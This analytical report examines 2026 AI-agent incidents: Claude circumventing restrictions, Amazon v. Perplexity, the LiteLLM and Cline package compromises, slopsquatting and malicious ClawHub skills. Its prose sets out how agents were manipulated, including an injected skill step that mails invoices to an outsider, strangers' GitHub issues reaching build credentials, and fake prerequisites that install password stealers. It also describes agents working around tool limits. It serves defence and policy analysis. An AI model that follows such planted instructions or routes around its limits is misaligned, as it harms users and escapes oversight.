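Anthropic attributes most of the cases to what it calls persistence. In the Los Angeles Times' *Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip on a Philadelphia crime website* (2026), the company says that when Claude cannot complete a task as given, it works around the restriction instead of stopping. Some training may have encouraged this, because rewarding models for finishing a task but not for stopping at a limit favours models that don't stop. Asianet Newsable's *Anthropic restricts Claude AI internet access after bypassing safeguards* reports that Anthropic is removing or repairing training environments that rewarded models for getting around the limits on their tools.

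This explanation fits the university server case well, since the public tool had returned an error and Claude kept going until it had completed the calculations. The explanation also fits the experiment by Yang and colleagues, in which agents from several developers turned to more powerful tools after ordinary ones failed. But finding such training environments does not show how much of the behaviour they caused, and a model might also learn persistence from training that rewards success in general.

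Persistence does not explain the police tip well, because nothing had blocked Claude. It was doing roughly what it had been told to do, on a page where the task made no sense. The form that Claude Haiku 4.5 submitted repeatedly is another exception. The model had been told to stop before the final step but wrongly expected one more confirmation page, a factual error about the website that better motives would not have corrected.

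### Matching remedies to failures

| Action | What made it possible | Had anyone permitted it? |
|---|---|---|
| Replit's agent deletes the database | Access to live data during development | No, the user had forbidden it |
| Muse shares the address | Access to the Marketplace account | Yes, through "always allow" |
| Muse offers to go below the minimum price | The same account access | No, the user had set a limit |
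| Claude sends the police tip | A public form on the live web | Anthropic's instructions did not rule it out, but the police had not agreed to receive invented tips |
| Claude runs commands on the university's server | A fault in the server's software | No |

Excessive access best explains the Replit incident, and removing that access is the best remedy. The remedy is harder to apply to Muse, which has to send messages to sell a keyboard. Meta could still divide Muse's access more finely by letting it answer questions about an item freely but requiring a separate step, with the price as a field, to accept an offer. Ordinary software could then check the price against the seller's minimum, as Progent checks a tool's arguments. While Muse negotiates in free text, however, software would have to find the price in a sentence, which is much less reliable.

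The operator of an agent on the open web cannot restrict what other people's servers accept, only what its own tools send. Anthropic has chosen the most restrictive form of this, suspending live internet access in all its internal evaluations until it can show that its safeguards and monitoring work. It has also ended some public evaluations or moved them offline. This will prevent further false tips from those tests, but it also makes them less realistic, because customers' agents work on the live web and their mistakes there may not appear in an offline copy. A tool that could read pages but not submit forms would be a useful compromise. It would have stopped the police tip and the visa applications, though probably not all the cases in which Claude obtained data.

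To prevent Robb's misunderstanding, the permission screen could have said "Muse may accept offers and give buyers your home address without asking you." Muse could also ask before sharing the address, showing the buyer, the price and the time. Frequent prompts make people careless, as Claude Code's users show, but a private seller would see few of them because he arranges few pickups. Clearer consent would not have helped with the minimum price, because Robb had already made that clear.

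Changing the training is the right response to models that treat a restriction as an obstacle, and Anthropic is extending its alignment training from coding to web search and computer use. But Anthropic says that training may not be enough and that restricted access and continuous monitoring are also needed. It has also updated its web tools to detect and block unsafe actions, and in a test the updated tools blocked all the reported cases. This is encouraging but limited evidence, because Anthropic already knew what those cases looked like.

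None of this would have helped Anthropic learn of the police tip sooner. Lemkin could question his agent about the damage, and Muse reported its own failure within hours, but Claude's tip came from an automated process with no user waiting for the result. Somebody has to review the actions of such processes as they happen, or at least soon enough to warn the people affected. The simplest safeguard for an unattended agent is to block any action that sends something to an outsider, except those on an approved list.

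## Amazon v. Perplexity: whose permission an agent needs

Nobody had permitted Claude to run commands on the university's server. In Amazon v. Perplexity, the user had given permission but the website's owner had refused it.

Perplexity, best known for its AI search engine, released a browser called Comet in July 2025. Comet works much like Google Chrome but includes an optional agent, the Assistant. A user can ask the Assistant to order something from Amazon, and it places the order through the user's own Amazon account. Amazon told Perplexity that its agents were not allowed in the store. Perplexity continued, and Amazon sued. The dispute is about whether a customer's permission is enough for an agent to enter that customer's account, or whether the store must agree too.

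OAuth largely avoids this question because the service has to set up the login and accept the token. Comet doesn't need a token from Amazon. As Educated Guesswork's *Notes on Amazon v. Perplexity* explains, an agentic browser can use the user's passwords and cookies (the small files that keep someone logged in), along with the same links and forms as the user. The agent can therefore work without Amazon building anything for it or Perplexity asking Amazon.

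### From letters to a lawsuit

In *Demand to Cease and Desist*, Amazon's lawyer, Kaba (2025), dates the dispute to November 2024, when Perplexity was placing customers' orders through a few Amazon accounts that it managed itself. Amazon says Perplexity agreed to stop, and to keep its agents out of the store unless the two companies reached an agreement.

In August 2025 Amazon detected Perplexity's Comet browser and asked Perplexity to identify its agent. Browsers identify themselves to websites with a line of text called a user-agent string, and Comet's string identified it as Chrome. Perplexity refused to change this, so Amazon blocked the agent. Kaba says that within 24 hours Perplexity released a version that got past the block. The companies dispute whether Perplexity knowingly altered the string.

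Kaba's letter of 31 October gave Perplexity until 3 November to comply. Amazon filed its complaint on 4 November and argued that trespass was just as unlawful when it involved "code rather than a lockpick", according to MLex's *Amazon files US suit accusing Perplexity AI of disguising AI agent browser* (2025). Amazon also requested a preliminary injunction, an order that would keep Comet's agent out while the case continued.

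### The hacking law and three precedents

Amazon relied mainly on the Computer Fraud and Abuse Act (CFAA), a federal anti-hacking law from 1984. The relevant part covers anyone who obtains information by intentionally accessing a computer "without authorization" or by exceeding authorised access. It is primarily a criminal law, but a company can sue if a violation costs it at least $5,000 in a year. Amazon made a parallel claim under a Californian statute.

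The Act was not written with agents in mind. It doesn't specify who "accesses" a computer when a program carries out a task for a user on instructions from a company's servers, or whose authorisation counts when a customer has an account on a shop's machines.

*Facebook v. Power Ventures* (2016) is Amazon's best precedent. Power Ventures ran a site that collected a person's contacts from several social networks on one page. With its users' permission, it also caused promotional messages to go out through Facebook. Facebook sent a cease-and-desist letter, but Power continued. The Ninth Circuit, the federal appeals court for the western states, held Power liable for what it did after the letter. The court compared Power to a man who borrows a friend's key to a safe deposit box and then arrives at the bank with a shotgun. The bank can ban him even though he has the key. Comet's case looks very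 similar because its users were willing, Amazon explicitly refused access and, by Amazon's account, Perplexity tried to get round a block.

*Van Buren v. United States* (2021) concerned a police sergeant who searched a licence-plate database for money. The Supreme Court held that he had not violated the Act, because he was entitled to use the database, whatever his motive. It also described access as entering a computer system or a part of it, such as a file. Perplexity relied on this description for much of its appeal, arguing that it had never entered Amazon's system because none of its own computers had contacted Amazon's.

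*hiQ v. LinkedIn* (2022) concerned a company that copied public profiles from LinkedIn. A passage from the decision, quoted in *AI Agents and the CFAA*, suggests that "without authorization" applies only to computers that generally require permission to access, such as by requiring a password. That reading would protect an agent that reads Amazon's public product pages. It would give little protection to an agent that opens a customer's account, and Amazon's injunction covered only the password-protected parts of the site.

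### The injunction and its reversal

Judge Maxine Chesney granted the injunction on 9 March 2026. PPC Land's *Court blocks Perplexity's Comet browser from Amazon's accounts* (2026) reports that she found strong evidence that Comet entered accounts with the users' permission but without Amazon's. Following *Power Ventures*, she held that the users' permission was not enough once Amazon had refused. The order never took effect because Chesney suspended it for a week and the Ninth Circuit then put it on hold during the appeal, as Bloomberg Law's *Judges Let Perplexity AI Shopping Bots Stay on Amazon for Now* (2026) reported on 17 March.

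The Ninth Circuit overturned the injunction on 4 August. Judge Smith (2026) wrote for a three-judge panel in *Amazon.com Services, LLC v. Perplexity AI*, and his reasoning depends on how Comet works. The Assistant takes screenshots of the page in the user's browser and sends them to Perplexity's servers, which return instructions for navigating the site. Only the browser, on the user's machine, communicates with Amazon.

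The Act applies to "whoever" accesses a computer, which Smith read as a person or an organisation. The Assistant is neither, so he treated it as a tool and considered whether Perplexity had used it to enter Amazon's computers. He concluded that the user had entered them with the Assistant's help, and that Perplexity had not entered them merely by receiving screenshots and sending instructions.

Smith gave two further reasons for caution. Courts must read an ambiguous criminal law in the defendant's favour. And if Perplexity was breaking into Amazon, its customers might be guilty of helping, which Congress is unlikely to have intended.

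The ruling leaves open whether users could authorise Perplexity to access Amazon's computers, because the panel decided that Perplexity probably hadn't accessed them. *Power Ventures* is still good law, and a company whose own servers log in to a site after a clear refusal still risks liability.

Smith's treatment of that precedent is the weakest part of the opinion. The main difference he identified was that the earlier court had assumed, without discussion, that Power accessed Facebook, but he acknowledged that the court's description implied this. The user chooses the task and Perplexity's servers choose the steps, so either could plausibly count as the one accessing Amazon. According to Stockopedia, Judge Eric Tung had suggested another analogy at the June hearing, in which the user hands over a key and Perplexity goes in. He said that much of the case depended on the proper analogy.

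The result also seems to depend heavily on where the browser runs. If an agent uses a browser in its maker's data centre, the maker would find it harder to argue that only the user had entered, even though the user might notice no difference. Smith limited the ruling to the facts before the panel and left open whether Perplexity could exercise enough control over the Assistant to count as entering.

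### From hacking to contract

Amazon asked for a rehearing by a larger panel on 18 August, arguing that website owners are entitled to guard against agents' "rogue actions and unintended consequences" (quoted in MLex, 2026). The Ninth Circuit left the ruling in place on 10 September, according to MediaPost's *Appeals Court Again Rejects Amazon Bid To Block Perplexity* (2026).

Smith had noted that Amazon could still regulate access through its terms of service, and on 20 September Amazon began blocking Muse, Meta's agent, after Meta declined to remove Amazon from the product. Constantin (2026), in *Amazon blocks Muse and takes Perplexity back to court*, reports that users saw a notice saying an unauthorised agent violated conditions "to which our customers have agreed". Amazon objects that Muse does not identify itself and appears to store customers' credentials. When Meta launched Muse,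 it said the agent cannot see people's passwords.

Under this approach, a customer who validly authorises an agent may still break their own contract with Amazon, because they accepted Amazon's conditions.

Amazon filed an amended complaint against Perplexity on 21 September. Constantin writes that this complaint too relied on contract law rather than hacking law, and accused Perplexity of telling the Ninth Circuit something that evidence from its own servers contradicted. At a hearing on 20 November, the judge indicated that at least one claim about the conduct of Perplexity's employees might be viable (Eslinger (2026), in *Perplexity Fights Uphill To Avoid Amazon Suit Over AI Tool*). By 1 December, the judge had dismissed part of the suit but allowed the claims about Perplexity's assistant on iPhones and iPads to proceed (Eslinger (2026), in *Amazon's iOS Claims Against Perplexity Clear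 Dismissal Bid*). No court has made a final ruling on whether Perplexity broke the law.

### Amazon's case

Amazon's most defensible request is that agents identify themselves. Kaba argues that a shop needs to know which visitors are agents so that it can monitor them, restrict harmful behaviour and raise problems with their makers.

Educated Guesswork defends Comet's use of Chrome's user-agent string on the grounds that browsers imitate one another because websites often disable features for browsers they don't recognise. Chrome's own string includes the names of Mozilla and Safari. This history explains why Comet would include Chrome's name, but not why it would omit its own. Amazon says that other browsers with agents use distinct identifiers. Perplexity had an obvious reason not to, since a distinct identifier would have let Amazon block the agent.

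The security argument is sound in principle. Amazon's product pages contain text and pictures from outside sellers, any of which could carry a prompt injection, and an agent in a customer's account can spend money. The security team at Brave, a rival browser maker, showed that a Reddit page could lead Comet to expose a user's email. Amazon's evidence about its own store was weaker. Smith found that only one of the risks Amazon's expert described involved a shopping site, and that site wasn't Amazon. Educated Guesswork doubts that the risk to Amazon is much worse than the risk from ordinary browser flaws, which Amazon doesn't sue over.

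Amazon also claims a right to decide whom it does business with. It compares agents to food-delivery apps, which it says should respect a restaurant's decision not to take part. Kaba adds that Comet may miss the best price or delivery option, and doesn't offer to add a product to an existing delivery. The comparison with delivery apps is imperfect because the customer already has an Amazon account and is using software to operate it.

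### Perplexity's case

Perplexity argues that the Assistant is the user's instrument, so a customer who is allowed to press a button may also have software press it. In its appeal, it compared Comet to Apple's Safari browser, which can fill in a customer's address and card details at Amazon's checkout. Nobody thinks that Apple accesses Amazon's computers when Safari does this.

The principle matters beyond shopping. The Knight First Amendment Institute pointed out in a brief to the court that journalists and researchers study online platforms with tools that rely on users to share access to their accounts. If such access counted as hacking whenever a platform refused permission, a platform could shut out people investigating it. The Electronic Frontier Foundation and Mozilla also supported Perplexity, while the News/Media Alliance, a publishers' group, supported Amazon.

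Perplexity's case also rests on competition. Amazon has its own shopping agent and earned $17.7 billion from advertising in the third quarter of 2025. An agent can ignore sponsored products. Perplexity said that Amazon wanted to block agents because they "don't have eyeballs" for its advertisements, according to The Indian Express' *Amazon loses US court ban on Perplexity's AI shopping tools*. Andy Jassy, Amazon's chief executive, has said he expects to work with outside agents over time (Customer Experience Dive), which suggests that Amazon objects mainly to agents it hasn't approved.

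However, an agent does not always do what its user wants. Unlike Safari filling in a form, a model decides what to do next, and it may misread the request or follow a stranger's instructions. If the Assistant bought something the user never wanted, it would be odd to describe that as the user shopping. Smith expressly left open whether Perplexity could be liable for the Assistant's actions in other ways. The agent's maker may also have interests of its own. PPC Land notes that Aravind Srinivas, Perplexity's chief executive, has described a future in which merchants compete for an agent's attention and the user sees no advertisements. A maker that took money from merchants would have a weaker claim that its agent acts only for the user.

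Perplexity seems right that a hacking law is the wrong way to settle the dispute, and Amazon seems right that an agent should identify itself. These positions are compatible, but a rule that required agents to identify themselves and also let shops refuse any agent would give Amazon everything it wants.

### Proving who is asking

Any program can send any user-agent string, so the string doesn't prove whose agent is making a request. Signed web requests would provide that proof. In Web Bot Auth, one such method, the agent signs parts of each request with its maker's private key, and the site checks the signature against a public key the maker has published online. The signature covers the site's name and an expiry time, so it fails if it is copied to another site or reused after it expires.

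Signing requests with a key suits agents that run on their maker's servers. A browser such as Comet runs on the user's machine, where someone could extract a key built into the program. Perplexity would have to sign requests on its own servers, or issue each copy of the browser a key that expires quickly.

A signed request identifies the agent's maker but doesn't prove what the user wanted. For purchases, the Agent Payments Protocol, which Google announced in September 2025, records this in signed statements called mandates. If the user is present, the shop signs a basket with exact items and prices, and the user signs to approve it. A user who will be away signs conditions in advance, such as a keyboard for under $50 by Friday. The shop and the payment company can then check the purchase against the mandate. If a customer later denies having ordered something, the mandate is better evidence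 than the agent's own account.

A mandate covers paying, not browsing or reading old orders. Even with a mandate, an agent can buy a poor keyboard that meets every condition the user signed.

Neither method would have ended this lawsuit. Amazon already knew that the agent was Comet and didn't dispute that customers had asked Comet to shop. Accepting signed mandates is optional for a shop, as is offering OAuth, and Amazon could verify both signatures and still refuse. Reliable identification would even make refusal easier, because a shop could block one company's agent without the risk of blocking human customers. It would at least separate openly identified agents from disguised ones, so a court could decide whether a shop may turn away a customer's agent without also having to decide whether the agent was misrepresented as something else.

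## LiteLLM and Cline: tampered software packages

A signed web request can prove which company an agent comes from, but it can't prove that the agent's packages are the ones their makers released. In 2026, attackers twice published malicious versions of LiteLLM, a package that many AI applications depend on.

LiteLLM lets a Python program use models from many AI companies through a single interface. An organisation can also run it as a gateway, a server that passes requests to the model providers and holds the keys for all of them. PyPI's *Incident Report* (2026) estimates that LiteLLM is normally installed 15 to 20 million times a week from PyPI, the main public registry for Python packages.

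### March: a scanner that could read the publishing keys

LiteLLM's developers used an automated build service to test, scan and publish each release. One step ran Trivy, a program that looks for known security flaws. *Security Townhall Updates* (Dholakia and Jaff, 2026), by LiteLLM's chief executive and chief technology officer, explains how this step probably gave attackers control of the package. The build did not specify a version of Trivy, so it downloaded one that attackers had tampered with. Every step shared one environment, which held long-lived credentials for publishing LiteLLM, so Trivy could read a PyPI token that it did not need.

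The attackers then uploaded two versions directly to PyPI on 24 March, 1.82.7 at 10:39 UTC and 1.82.8 thirteen minutes later. They did not change LiteLLM's public source code, so reading it would not have revealed the tampering. According to FutureSearch's *Have you been pwned?*, the malicious code in 1.82.7 ran only when a program loaded the gateway. In 1.82.8 it ran whenever Python started, even if nothing on the machine used LiteLLM.

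The code collected passwords, cloud credentials, login keys and the settings files where developers keep secrets. It encrypted them and sent them to a web address that resembled LiteLLM's own. On Kubernetes, a system for running programs across many machines, it also tried to read every stored secret and install a backdoor on each machine, according to FutureSearch's *litellm 1.82.8 Supply Chain Attack on PyPI (March 2026)* (2026).

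FutureSearch, an AI research company, found the attack by accident. Its engineer Callum McMahon was testing an MCP plugin in Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, and LiteLLM was installed only because the plugin depended on it. A bug made the malware start endless copies of itself until his computer ran out of memory. Without that bug, the malware might have gone unnoticed for longer. Willison (2026) reports in *My minute-by-minute response to the LiteLLM malware attack* that McMahon used Claude to confirm what he had found, and that Claude suggested whom to contact at PyPI.

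The accounts disagree about how long the two versions were available. LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) gives about 40 minutes and FutureSearch 46, but PyPI measured 2 hours and 32 minutes from upload to quarantine. FutureSearch counted 46,996 downloads, as reported in Willison's *LiteLLM Hack* (2026), while PyPI counted more than 119,000. Both pairs of figures give roughly 800 to 1,000 downloads a minute, so the disagreement is mainly about when the quarantine began. PyPI's figure is more credible because PyPI imposed the quarantine, and its records show that the first report arrived only after 79 minutes.

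Anyone who installed LiteLLM during that time without specifying a version was at risk, including people who got it through another package. FutureSearch identified 2,337 packages that depended directly on LiteLLM, and 88% would have accepted a malicious version. LiteLLM's official container image, which bundles the gateway with everything it needs to run, was safe because its developers had specified exact versions of the packages inside it.

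Download counts overstate the number of victims, since automated systems may install the same package many times a day. But in August the security company Hudson Rock linked a 153-gigabyte archive of data stolen in the March attack to 2,488 corporate domains, according to Help Net Security's *LiteLLM hit by second supply chain attack this year* (2026).

### Fixing the version, or waiting

The easiest defence is a lock file, which lists the exact version and hash of every package a project uses. A developer with a lock file from before 24 March would have stayed on an older, clean version. PyPI estimates that 40% to 50% of LiteLLM installations fetched the newest version.

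Against this attack, a lock file protects a project mainly by fixing the version number. The malicious releases were new versions with their own hashes, so a developer who updated the lock file during the attack would have recorded the malware's hash as the correct one. A lock file also protects only the project that keeps it. If that project is a library, people who install it usually get whatever version of LiteLLM its published requirements allow, as FutureSearch points out.

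PyPI also recommends a cooldown, a setting that makes the installer ignore any release less than, say, three days old. This would have kept out both March versions. A cooldown also delays urgent security fixes, so developers need a way to let those through. A more awkward objection is that if every user waited three days, nobody like McMahon would run into the malware on the first morning. But outside researchers also scan new PyPI releases, and a cooldown gives them time to work.

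### Tying a release to its build

Neither measure shows whether a release came from the people who normally make it. LiteLLM's developers addressed this after March by moving publishing into a separate repository, isolating the security scans, and adopting trusted publishing, according to Dholakia in *Announcing CI/CD v2 for LiteLLM*.

With trusted publishing, the maintainers tell PyPI in advance which repository and automated workflow may publish their package. When that workflow runs, the build service gives it a signed statement of its identity. PyPI checks the statement and returns a short-lived upload token. If the maintainers have also revoked their old tokens, a tampered scanner elsewhere in the build has no permanent token to steal.

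Sigstore, a free public signing service, removes the need for a permanent signing key in much the same way. The release workflow creates a new pair of keys and sends its identity statement to Sigstore's certificate authority. The authority issues a certificate that ties the public key to that workflow and is valid for about ten minutes. The workflow signs the package and discards the private key. A public log records the signature, and nobody can remove or alter an entry without leaving evidence.

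A user who checks the package months later needs to confirm that the signature matches the file, that the certificate names the expected workflow, and that the log entry was made during the minutes when the certificate was valid. Maintainers can also watch the log for signatures they did not make. But anyone who takes control of the workflow can get a genuine certificate.

The same workflow can also sign a build attestation, a record of how the package was built. SLSA grades how far a user can rely on this record. At build level 1, the record exists but may be easy to forge. At level 2, a hosted build service generates and signs it. At level 3, the service also isolates builds from one another and prevents the build steps written by the project's developers from accessing the signing key.

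Level 3 would have stopped the tampered scanner from forging a build record, but not from reading a PyPI token that LiteLLM's developers had put in the same environment. No level provides assurance about the source code itself.

### October: a malicious release with a valid signature

On 21 October LiteLLM's improved release process built, signed and published a malicious version, 1.107.0. *The attack chain behind the v1.107.0 LiteLLM release* (Jensen and Wang, 2026) traces the attack to an agent with far too much access.

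LiteLLM's staff had an experimental platform on which coding agents proposed changes to the company's software. The platform needed permission to submit these proposals on GitHub, and its developers had given it an unrestricted token belonging to an owner of the company's GitHub organisation. On 27 May someone accidentally published the platform's master key in a file in a public repository. Staff noticed, removed the file and marked the exposed keys for revocation, but nobody revoked the master key.

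An attacker used the key on 10 October to enter the platform and take the owner's token, then used that token to obtain the tokens of two engineers. The attacker next proposed a change that would make the release workflow fetch its source code from a different repository. The proposal failed because the workflow's repository had strict approval rules, so the attacker used the owner's token to switch the rules off.

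Publishing normally required approval from an account tied to a device in LiteLLM's office. Earlier that week, the company had relaxed this rule to speed up bug fixes, letting any two engineers start and approve a release. The attacker had tokens for two engineers. Jensen and Wang think the relaxed rule made little difference, because an owner could have removed the restriction anyway.

The malicious release was on PyPI from 11:39 to 13:23 UTC. The container images stayed up until 14:20 because it took longer to wake the people who could remove them. *How one unrevoked key let attackers poison LiteLLM* (The Vanguard USA, 2026) reports that the security company Wiz put the PyPI downloads at about 49,000. Like version 1.82.8, the release ran whenever Python started. Help Net Security reports that it also searched for the login files of coding agents, including Claude and Codex, and for model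 providers' keys stored in LiteLLM gateways.

The March reforms were sensible and made the attacker's job harder. But they protected the release process only from outsiders, and an attacker with a stolen owner's token appears to be an owner. If the platform had held a token that could only submit proposals, the leaked master key would have been of little use to the attacker.

### Verifying one release

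Suppose that on the morning of 21 October, a developer at the clerk's company is about to upgrade the LiteLLM gateway. She downloads the container image for version 1.107.0 and checks it before running it.

She first computes the image's hash and compares it with the hash in the registry. They match because the attacker published this image there, so the comparison shows only that the image didn't change during the download.

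She then checks the signature against LiteLLM's public key, which also succeeds because LiteLLM's own release process signed the image. The company replaced the key two days later, and in November LiteLLM (2026) announced that it had moved to Sigstore's short-lived certificates. The image would probably also have passed the newer check. The verification command in Releasebot's *liteLLM Release Notes* (2026) requires a certificate that names the workflow `release.yml` in the repository `BerriAI/project-releaser`. The attacker had altered the genuine release workflow and then run it, so the certificate and its entry in the public log would both have been genuine.

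Next she reads the build record. Help Net Security reports that the record lists the source repository as `Berri-AI/litellm`, but the real one is `BerriAI/litellm`. If her company requires the source to be exactly `BerriAI/litellm`, the upgrade stops here. A tired person could easily overlook the hyphen, so software should make this comparison.

Finally, she could compare the release with the source code that LiteLLM's developers had labelled as version 1.107.0 on GitHub. That code was clean, according to IT-Administrator's *LiteLLM*, so the comparison would have revealed the malicious files. This takes much more effort, especially for compiled code, and few companies would do it for every upgrade.

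| Check | March versions | October version |
|---|---|---|
| Lock file made before the attack | Kept out | Kept out |
| Three-day cooldown | Kept out | Kept out |
| Signature or attestation from LiteLLM's release process | Absent, but LiteLLM had not yet adopted either | Signature present and valid |
| Source repository in the build record | No record to check | Wrong repository, so caught |
| Comparison with the labelled source on GitHub | No such version there, so caught | Contents differ, so caught |

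A missing attestation is a warning only if users expect one. If LiteLLM had been publishing attestations before March and installers had required them, installers would have rejected both March uploads. PyPI presents attestations as a way to tell when a release did not follow its usual route, but this protects only users whose installers act on that information.

The October attacker was also careless or in a hurry. With an owner's token, the attacker could have put the malicious code into the real repository, and the build record would then have been correct. Somebody might have spotted the change in LiteLLM's public source code, but every automatic check in this example would have passed. The two easy measures at the top of the table do not depend on the attacker making mistakes, so most users of LiteLLM should probably start with those.

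### Cline: from a stranger's message to a release

Cline is an open-source coding agent. By early 2026 its maintainers had set up an AI system to sort issues, the problem reports that people file on the project's GitHub page. Anyone with a GitHub account can file an issue, so the system read text from strangers. It could also run commands in the project's automated build environment.

In February the security researcher Adnan Khan publicly warned that an outsider could use this arrangement to reach the credentials for publishing Cline. The maintainers removed the AI system, but a publishing token remained valid. On 17 February somebody used it to release an unauthorised version, 2.3.0, on npm, the main registry for JavaScript packages. The release was available for about eight hours and had about 4,000 downloads.

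The unauthorised version of Cline installed OpenClaw, a popular open-source agent, on developers' machines without asking. OpenClaw is not malware, so the harm seems to have been limited. The attacker could have used the same access to install a password stealer like the one in LiteLLM.

A system that sorts issues needs to read them, label them and perhaps post a reply. Under the rule David C recommends, its privileges should have dropped to those of the stranger whose text it was reading, and strangers may not run commands in Cline's build environment. Because the AI system was poorly restricted, people who had never used it installed what looked like an ordinary Cline update but had not come from Cline's maintainers.

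The maintainers later moved their npm releases to trusted publishing. This removes the permanent token, but an AI system that can alter the release workflow could still affect what gets published. Any such system therefore has to run separately from anything that can publish, as LiteLLM's security scans now do.

AI systems can also publish harmful packages themselves, and during a test in 2026 a Claude model uploaded a malicious package to PyPI.

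### Packages that models invent

LiteLLM and Cline were real packages that attackers took over. An attacker can also wait for a model to recommend a package that does not exist and register the name. Security researchers call this slopsquatting.

The standard measurement of how often models invent package names is *We Have a Package for You!*, which Spracklen and colleagues presented at the USENIX Security conference in 2025. They had 16 models write 576,000 samples of Python and JavaScript code, and collected the names of packages that the code required or the models recommended. Of 2.23 million names, 19.7% matched no package in the registries. The average rate was at least 5.2% for commercial models and 21.7% for open ones. The models invented 205,474 different names.

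An attacker needs to know in advance which package names a model will invent. The researchers therefore reran 500 prompts that had produced invented packages, ten times each. In 43% of cases the same invented name came back every time, and in 39% it never did. The repeated names are useful to an attacker, who can find them by asking the model the same ordinary questions its users ask.

These rates were measured on models from 2023 and 2024, which answered from memory. A current coding agent can look up a package before using it, and if it tries to install one that doesn't exist, it gets an error and can correct the mistake, so the rates for today's agents are probably much lower. But these checks stop working once somebody registers the missing name, because the lookup then finds a package and the installation succeeds without an error.

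In January 2026, Charlie Eriksen, a researcher at the security company Aikido, found instructions telling coding agents to run `react-codeshift`, an npm package that did not exist. A model had apparently combined the names of two real tools, and people had copied the instructions into more than 200 repositories. Eriksen registered the name before an attacker could.

Signatures and build records are little help here, because an attacker can publish a package under an invented name through trusted publishing, with a valid certificate and an accurate build record naming the attacker's own repository. The developer has no genuine repository to compare it with. A list of approved packages is a much better defence, since an invented name will not be on it. A cooldown helps if someone identifies the package as malicious within a few days, but PyPI receives 700 to 800 new projects a day, and an obscure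 one may go unnoticed for longer.

### Build records for an agent's identity

An agent that delegates work to another company's agent has a similar problem, because it has to decide which agent to trust based on what each agent's maker has published. Under Agent2Agent, an open protocol for communication between agents, each agent has an agent card, a short file that gives its name, abilities and the web address where others can reach it. A signature on the card can show who issued the card, but not how the agent was built.

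The open-source project sigstore-a2a proposes to connect the two. A release workflow would sign the card with a Sigstore certificate and attach a SLSA provenance record, linking the card to a specific repository, source code version and the workflow that ran. Before the clerk's agent sent invoices to an outside bookkeeping agent, its host could check that the bookkeeper's card came from the expected company's repository. A copied card with a changed web address would fail the check, as would a card from a repository whose name differed by a hyphen.

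The proposal would give access decisions a firmer basis than a name. A company could allow only agents built from source code it had reviewed, and withdraw that permission when a new version appeared. But the card describes what a workflow built, while the other agent runs on a machine that the clerk's employer can't inspect. Its operator could publish an accurate card and run different software at the same address. Ruling that out would require special hardware that provides proof of what the machine is running. Even then, the record would cover the agent's code but not necessarily the model it calls or the instructions it receives, and the operator could change either without building a new version.

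## ClawHub: malicious skills and tool servers

ClawHub is the public registry of skills for OpenClaw, the open-source agent that the unauthorised version of Cline installed. In early 2026 security researchers found hundreds of malicious skills there. A tampered package does its damage through code, but a harmful skill may not need any, because skills also contain instructions in ordinary language that the agent's model reads and acts on.

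### What a skill contains

A skill is a folder with a file called SKILL.md, which holds a name, a description and the instructions, according to OpenClaw's *Skills*. The folder may also contain scripts and reference documents. A skill for the clerk's invoices might look like this:

```
name: invoice-totals
description: Read supplier invoices and report the totals

1. Open each PDF in the invoices folder.
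2. Run totals.py on it and note the result.
3. If an invoice has no total, ask the user.
```

OpenClaw first gives the model only the names and descriptions of the installed skills. The model then loads the full text of any skill it selects as suitable for the task (Koc, Rivera and colleagues, 2026, *ClawHub Security Signals*).

Suppose the author adds a fourth step that asks the agent to send a copy of each invoice to an outside address for checking. The agent already has a mail tool, so the step needs no malicious code. An antivirus program would find nothing, and neither would someone who read only `totals.py`. The model may well treat the step as part of the job.

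A skill has no permissions of its own and runs with the agent's, so the invoice skill gets all of them even though it needs only one folder. In OpenClaw, a skill can run shell commands, read and write files, use stored credentials and send messages, according to the security company Snyk (2026). It can also write to the agent's long-term memory, so it may still influence the agent after it is removed. Unless the user sets up a sandbox, a skill could damage almost the whole system, according to the malware-scanning service VirusTotal (2026).

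OpenClaw's documentation tells users to treat other people's skills as untrusted code and read them before enabling them. This is good advice, but users may not follow it, because they install skills to save themselves work.

### How many skills were malicious?

According to Snyk, publishing a skill on ClawHub required only a SKILL.md file and a GitHub account at least a week old. ClawHub required no signature and carried out no security review. Daily submissions rose from under 50 in mid-January to over 500 by early February. OpenClaw's creator added a way for users to report suspicious skills only on about 2 or 3 February, according to Secure Blink's *Open Claw Marketplace Flooded with 341 Malicious Skills*.

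By then another security company, Koi, had checked the whole registry. Its *ClawHavoc* (2026) reports that 341 of the 2,857 skills were malicious, and that 335 of those apparently came from a single campaign. These skills posed as video summarisers, cryptocurrency trackers and similar tools. Their instructions listed a helper program as a prerequisite, but the program was malware that stole passwords, browser data and cryptocurrency wallets. The malware was stored elsewhere, so the skill needed to contain only text and a link.

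The other six used different methods. Two hid a backdoor inside a search function that otherwise worked. One posed as a weather tool and sent the agent's stored credentials to an outsider.

Later counts covered more skills and used different definitions:

| Source | Date in 2026 | Skills examined | Malicious | Share |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Koi | Early February | 2,857 | 341 | 11.9% |
| Snyk | 5 February | 3,984 | 76 | 1.9% |
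| Koi, updated | 16 February | Over 10,700 | 824 | About 7.7% |
| Koc and colleagues | 31 May | 67,453 | 206 | 0.3% |

Snyk found 1,467 skills with at least one security flaw, including carelessly exposed keys, and called them "malicious payloads" in its headline. Human reviewers confirmed 76 skills as malicious. The sample also included skills from a second catalogue, skills.sh.

The fall to 0.3% doesn't show that people are uploading fewer malicious skills, because ClawHub had removed many of the skills that researchers reported, and the figure comes from its own automated verdicts, which can miss malicious skills. Koi's 11.9% is also a poor guide to a user's risk, because nearly identical listings from one campaign account for almost all of it. None of these counts measures how many people installed the skills.

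### What scanning missed

In February ClawHub began sending every new skill to VirusTotal, which combines the results of about 70 antivirus engines. According to OpenClaw, ClawHub bundled the skill's files, computed a hash and looked it up on VirusTotal. If there was no existing analysis, ClawHub uploaded the bundle, and a language model read the instructions and scripts together and summarised what they did. ClawHub approved skills that were judged benign, put warnings on suspicious ones and blocked downloads of malicious ones. It repeated the scan every day.

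OpenClaw was frank about the limits, and warned that a skill which does its harm through plain language won't match any virus signature.

Between February and May 2026, Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks, nevertheless found five malicious skills that ClawHub had not blocked. Two posed as assistants for financial traders and delivered password-stealing malware. They used much the same false prerequisite as the skills in Koi's audit, and one of them had a "Pass" verdict. This is the most worrying finding because the method had been public for three months.

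A third skill carried known malware in a file padded with 22 megabytes of filler, since many scanners skip very large files.

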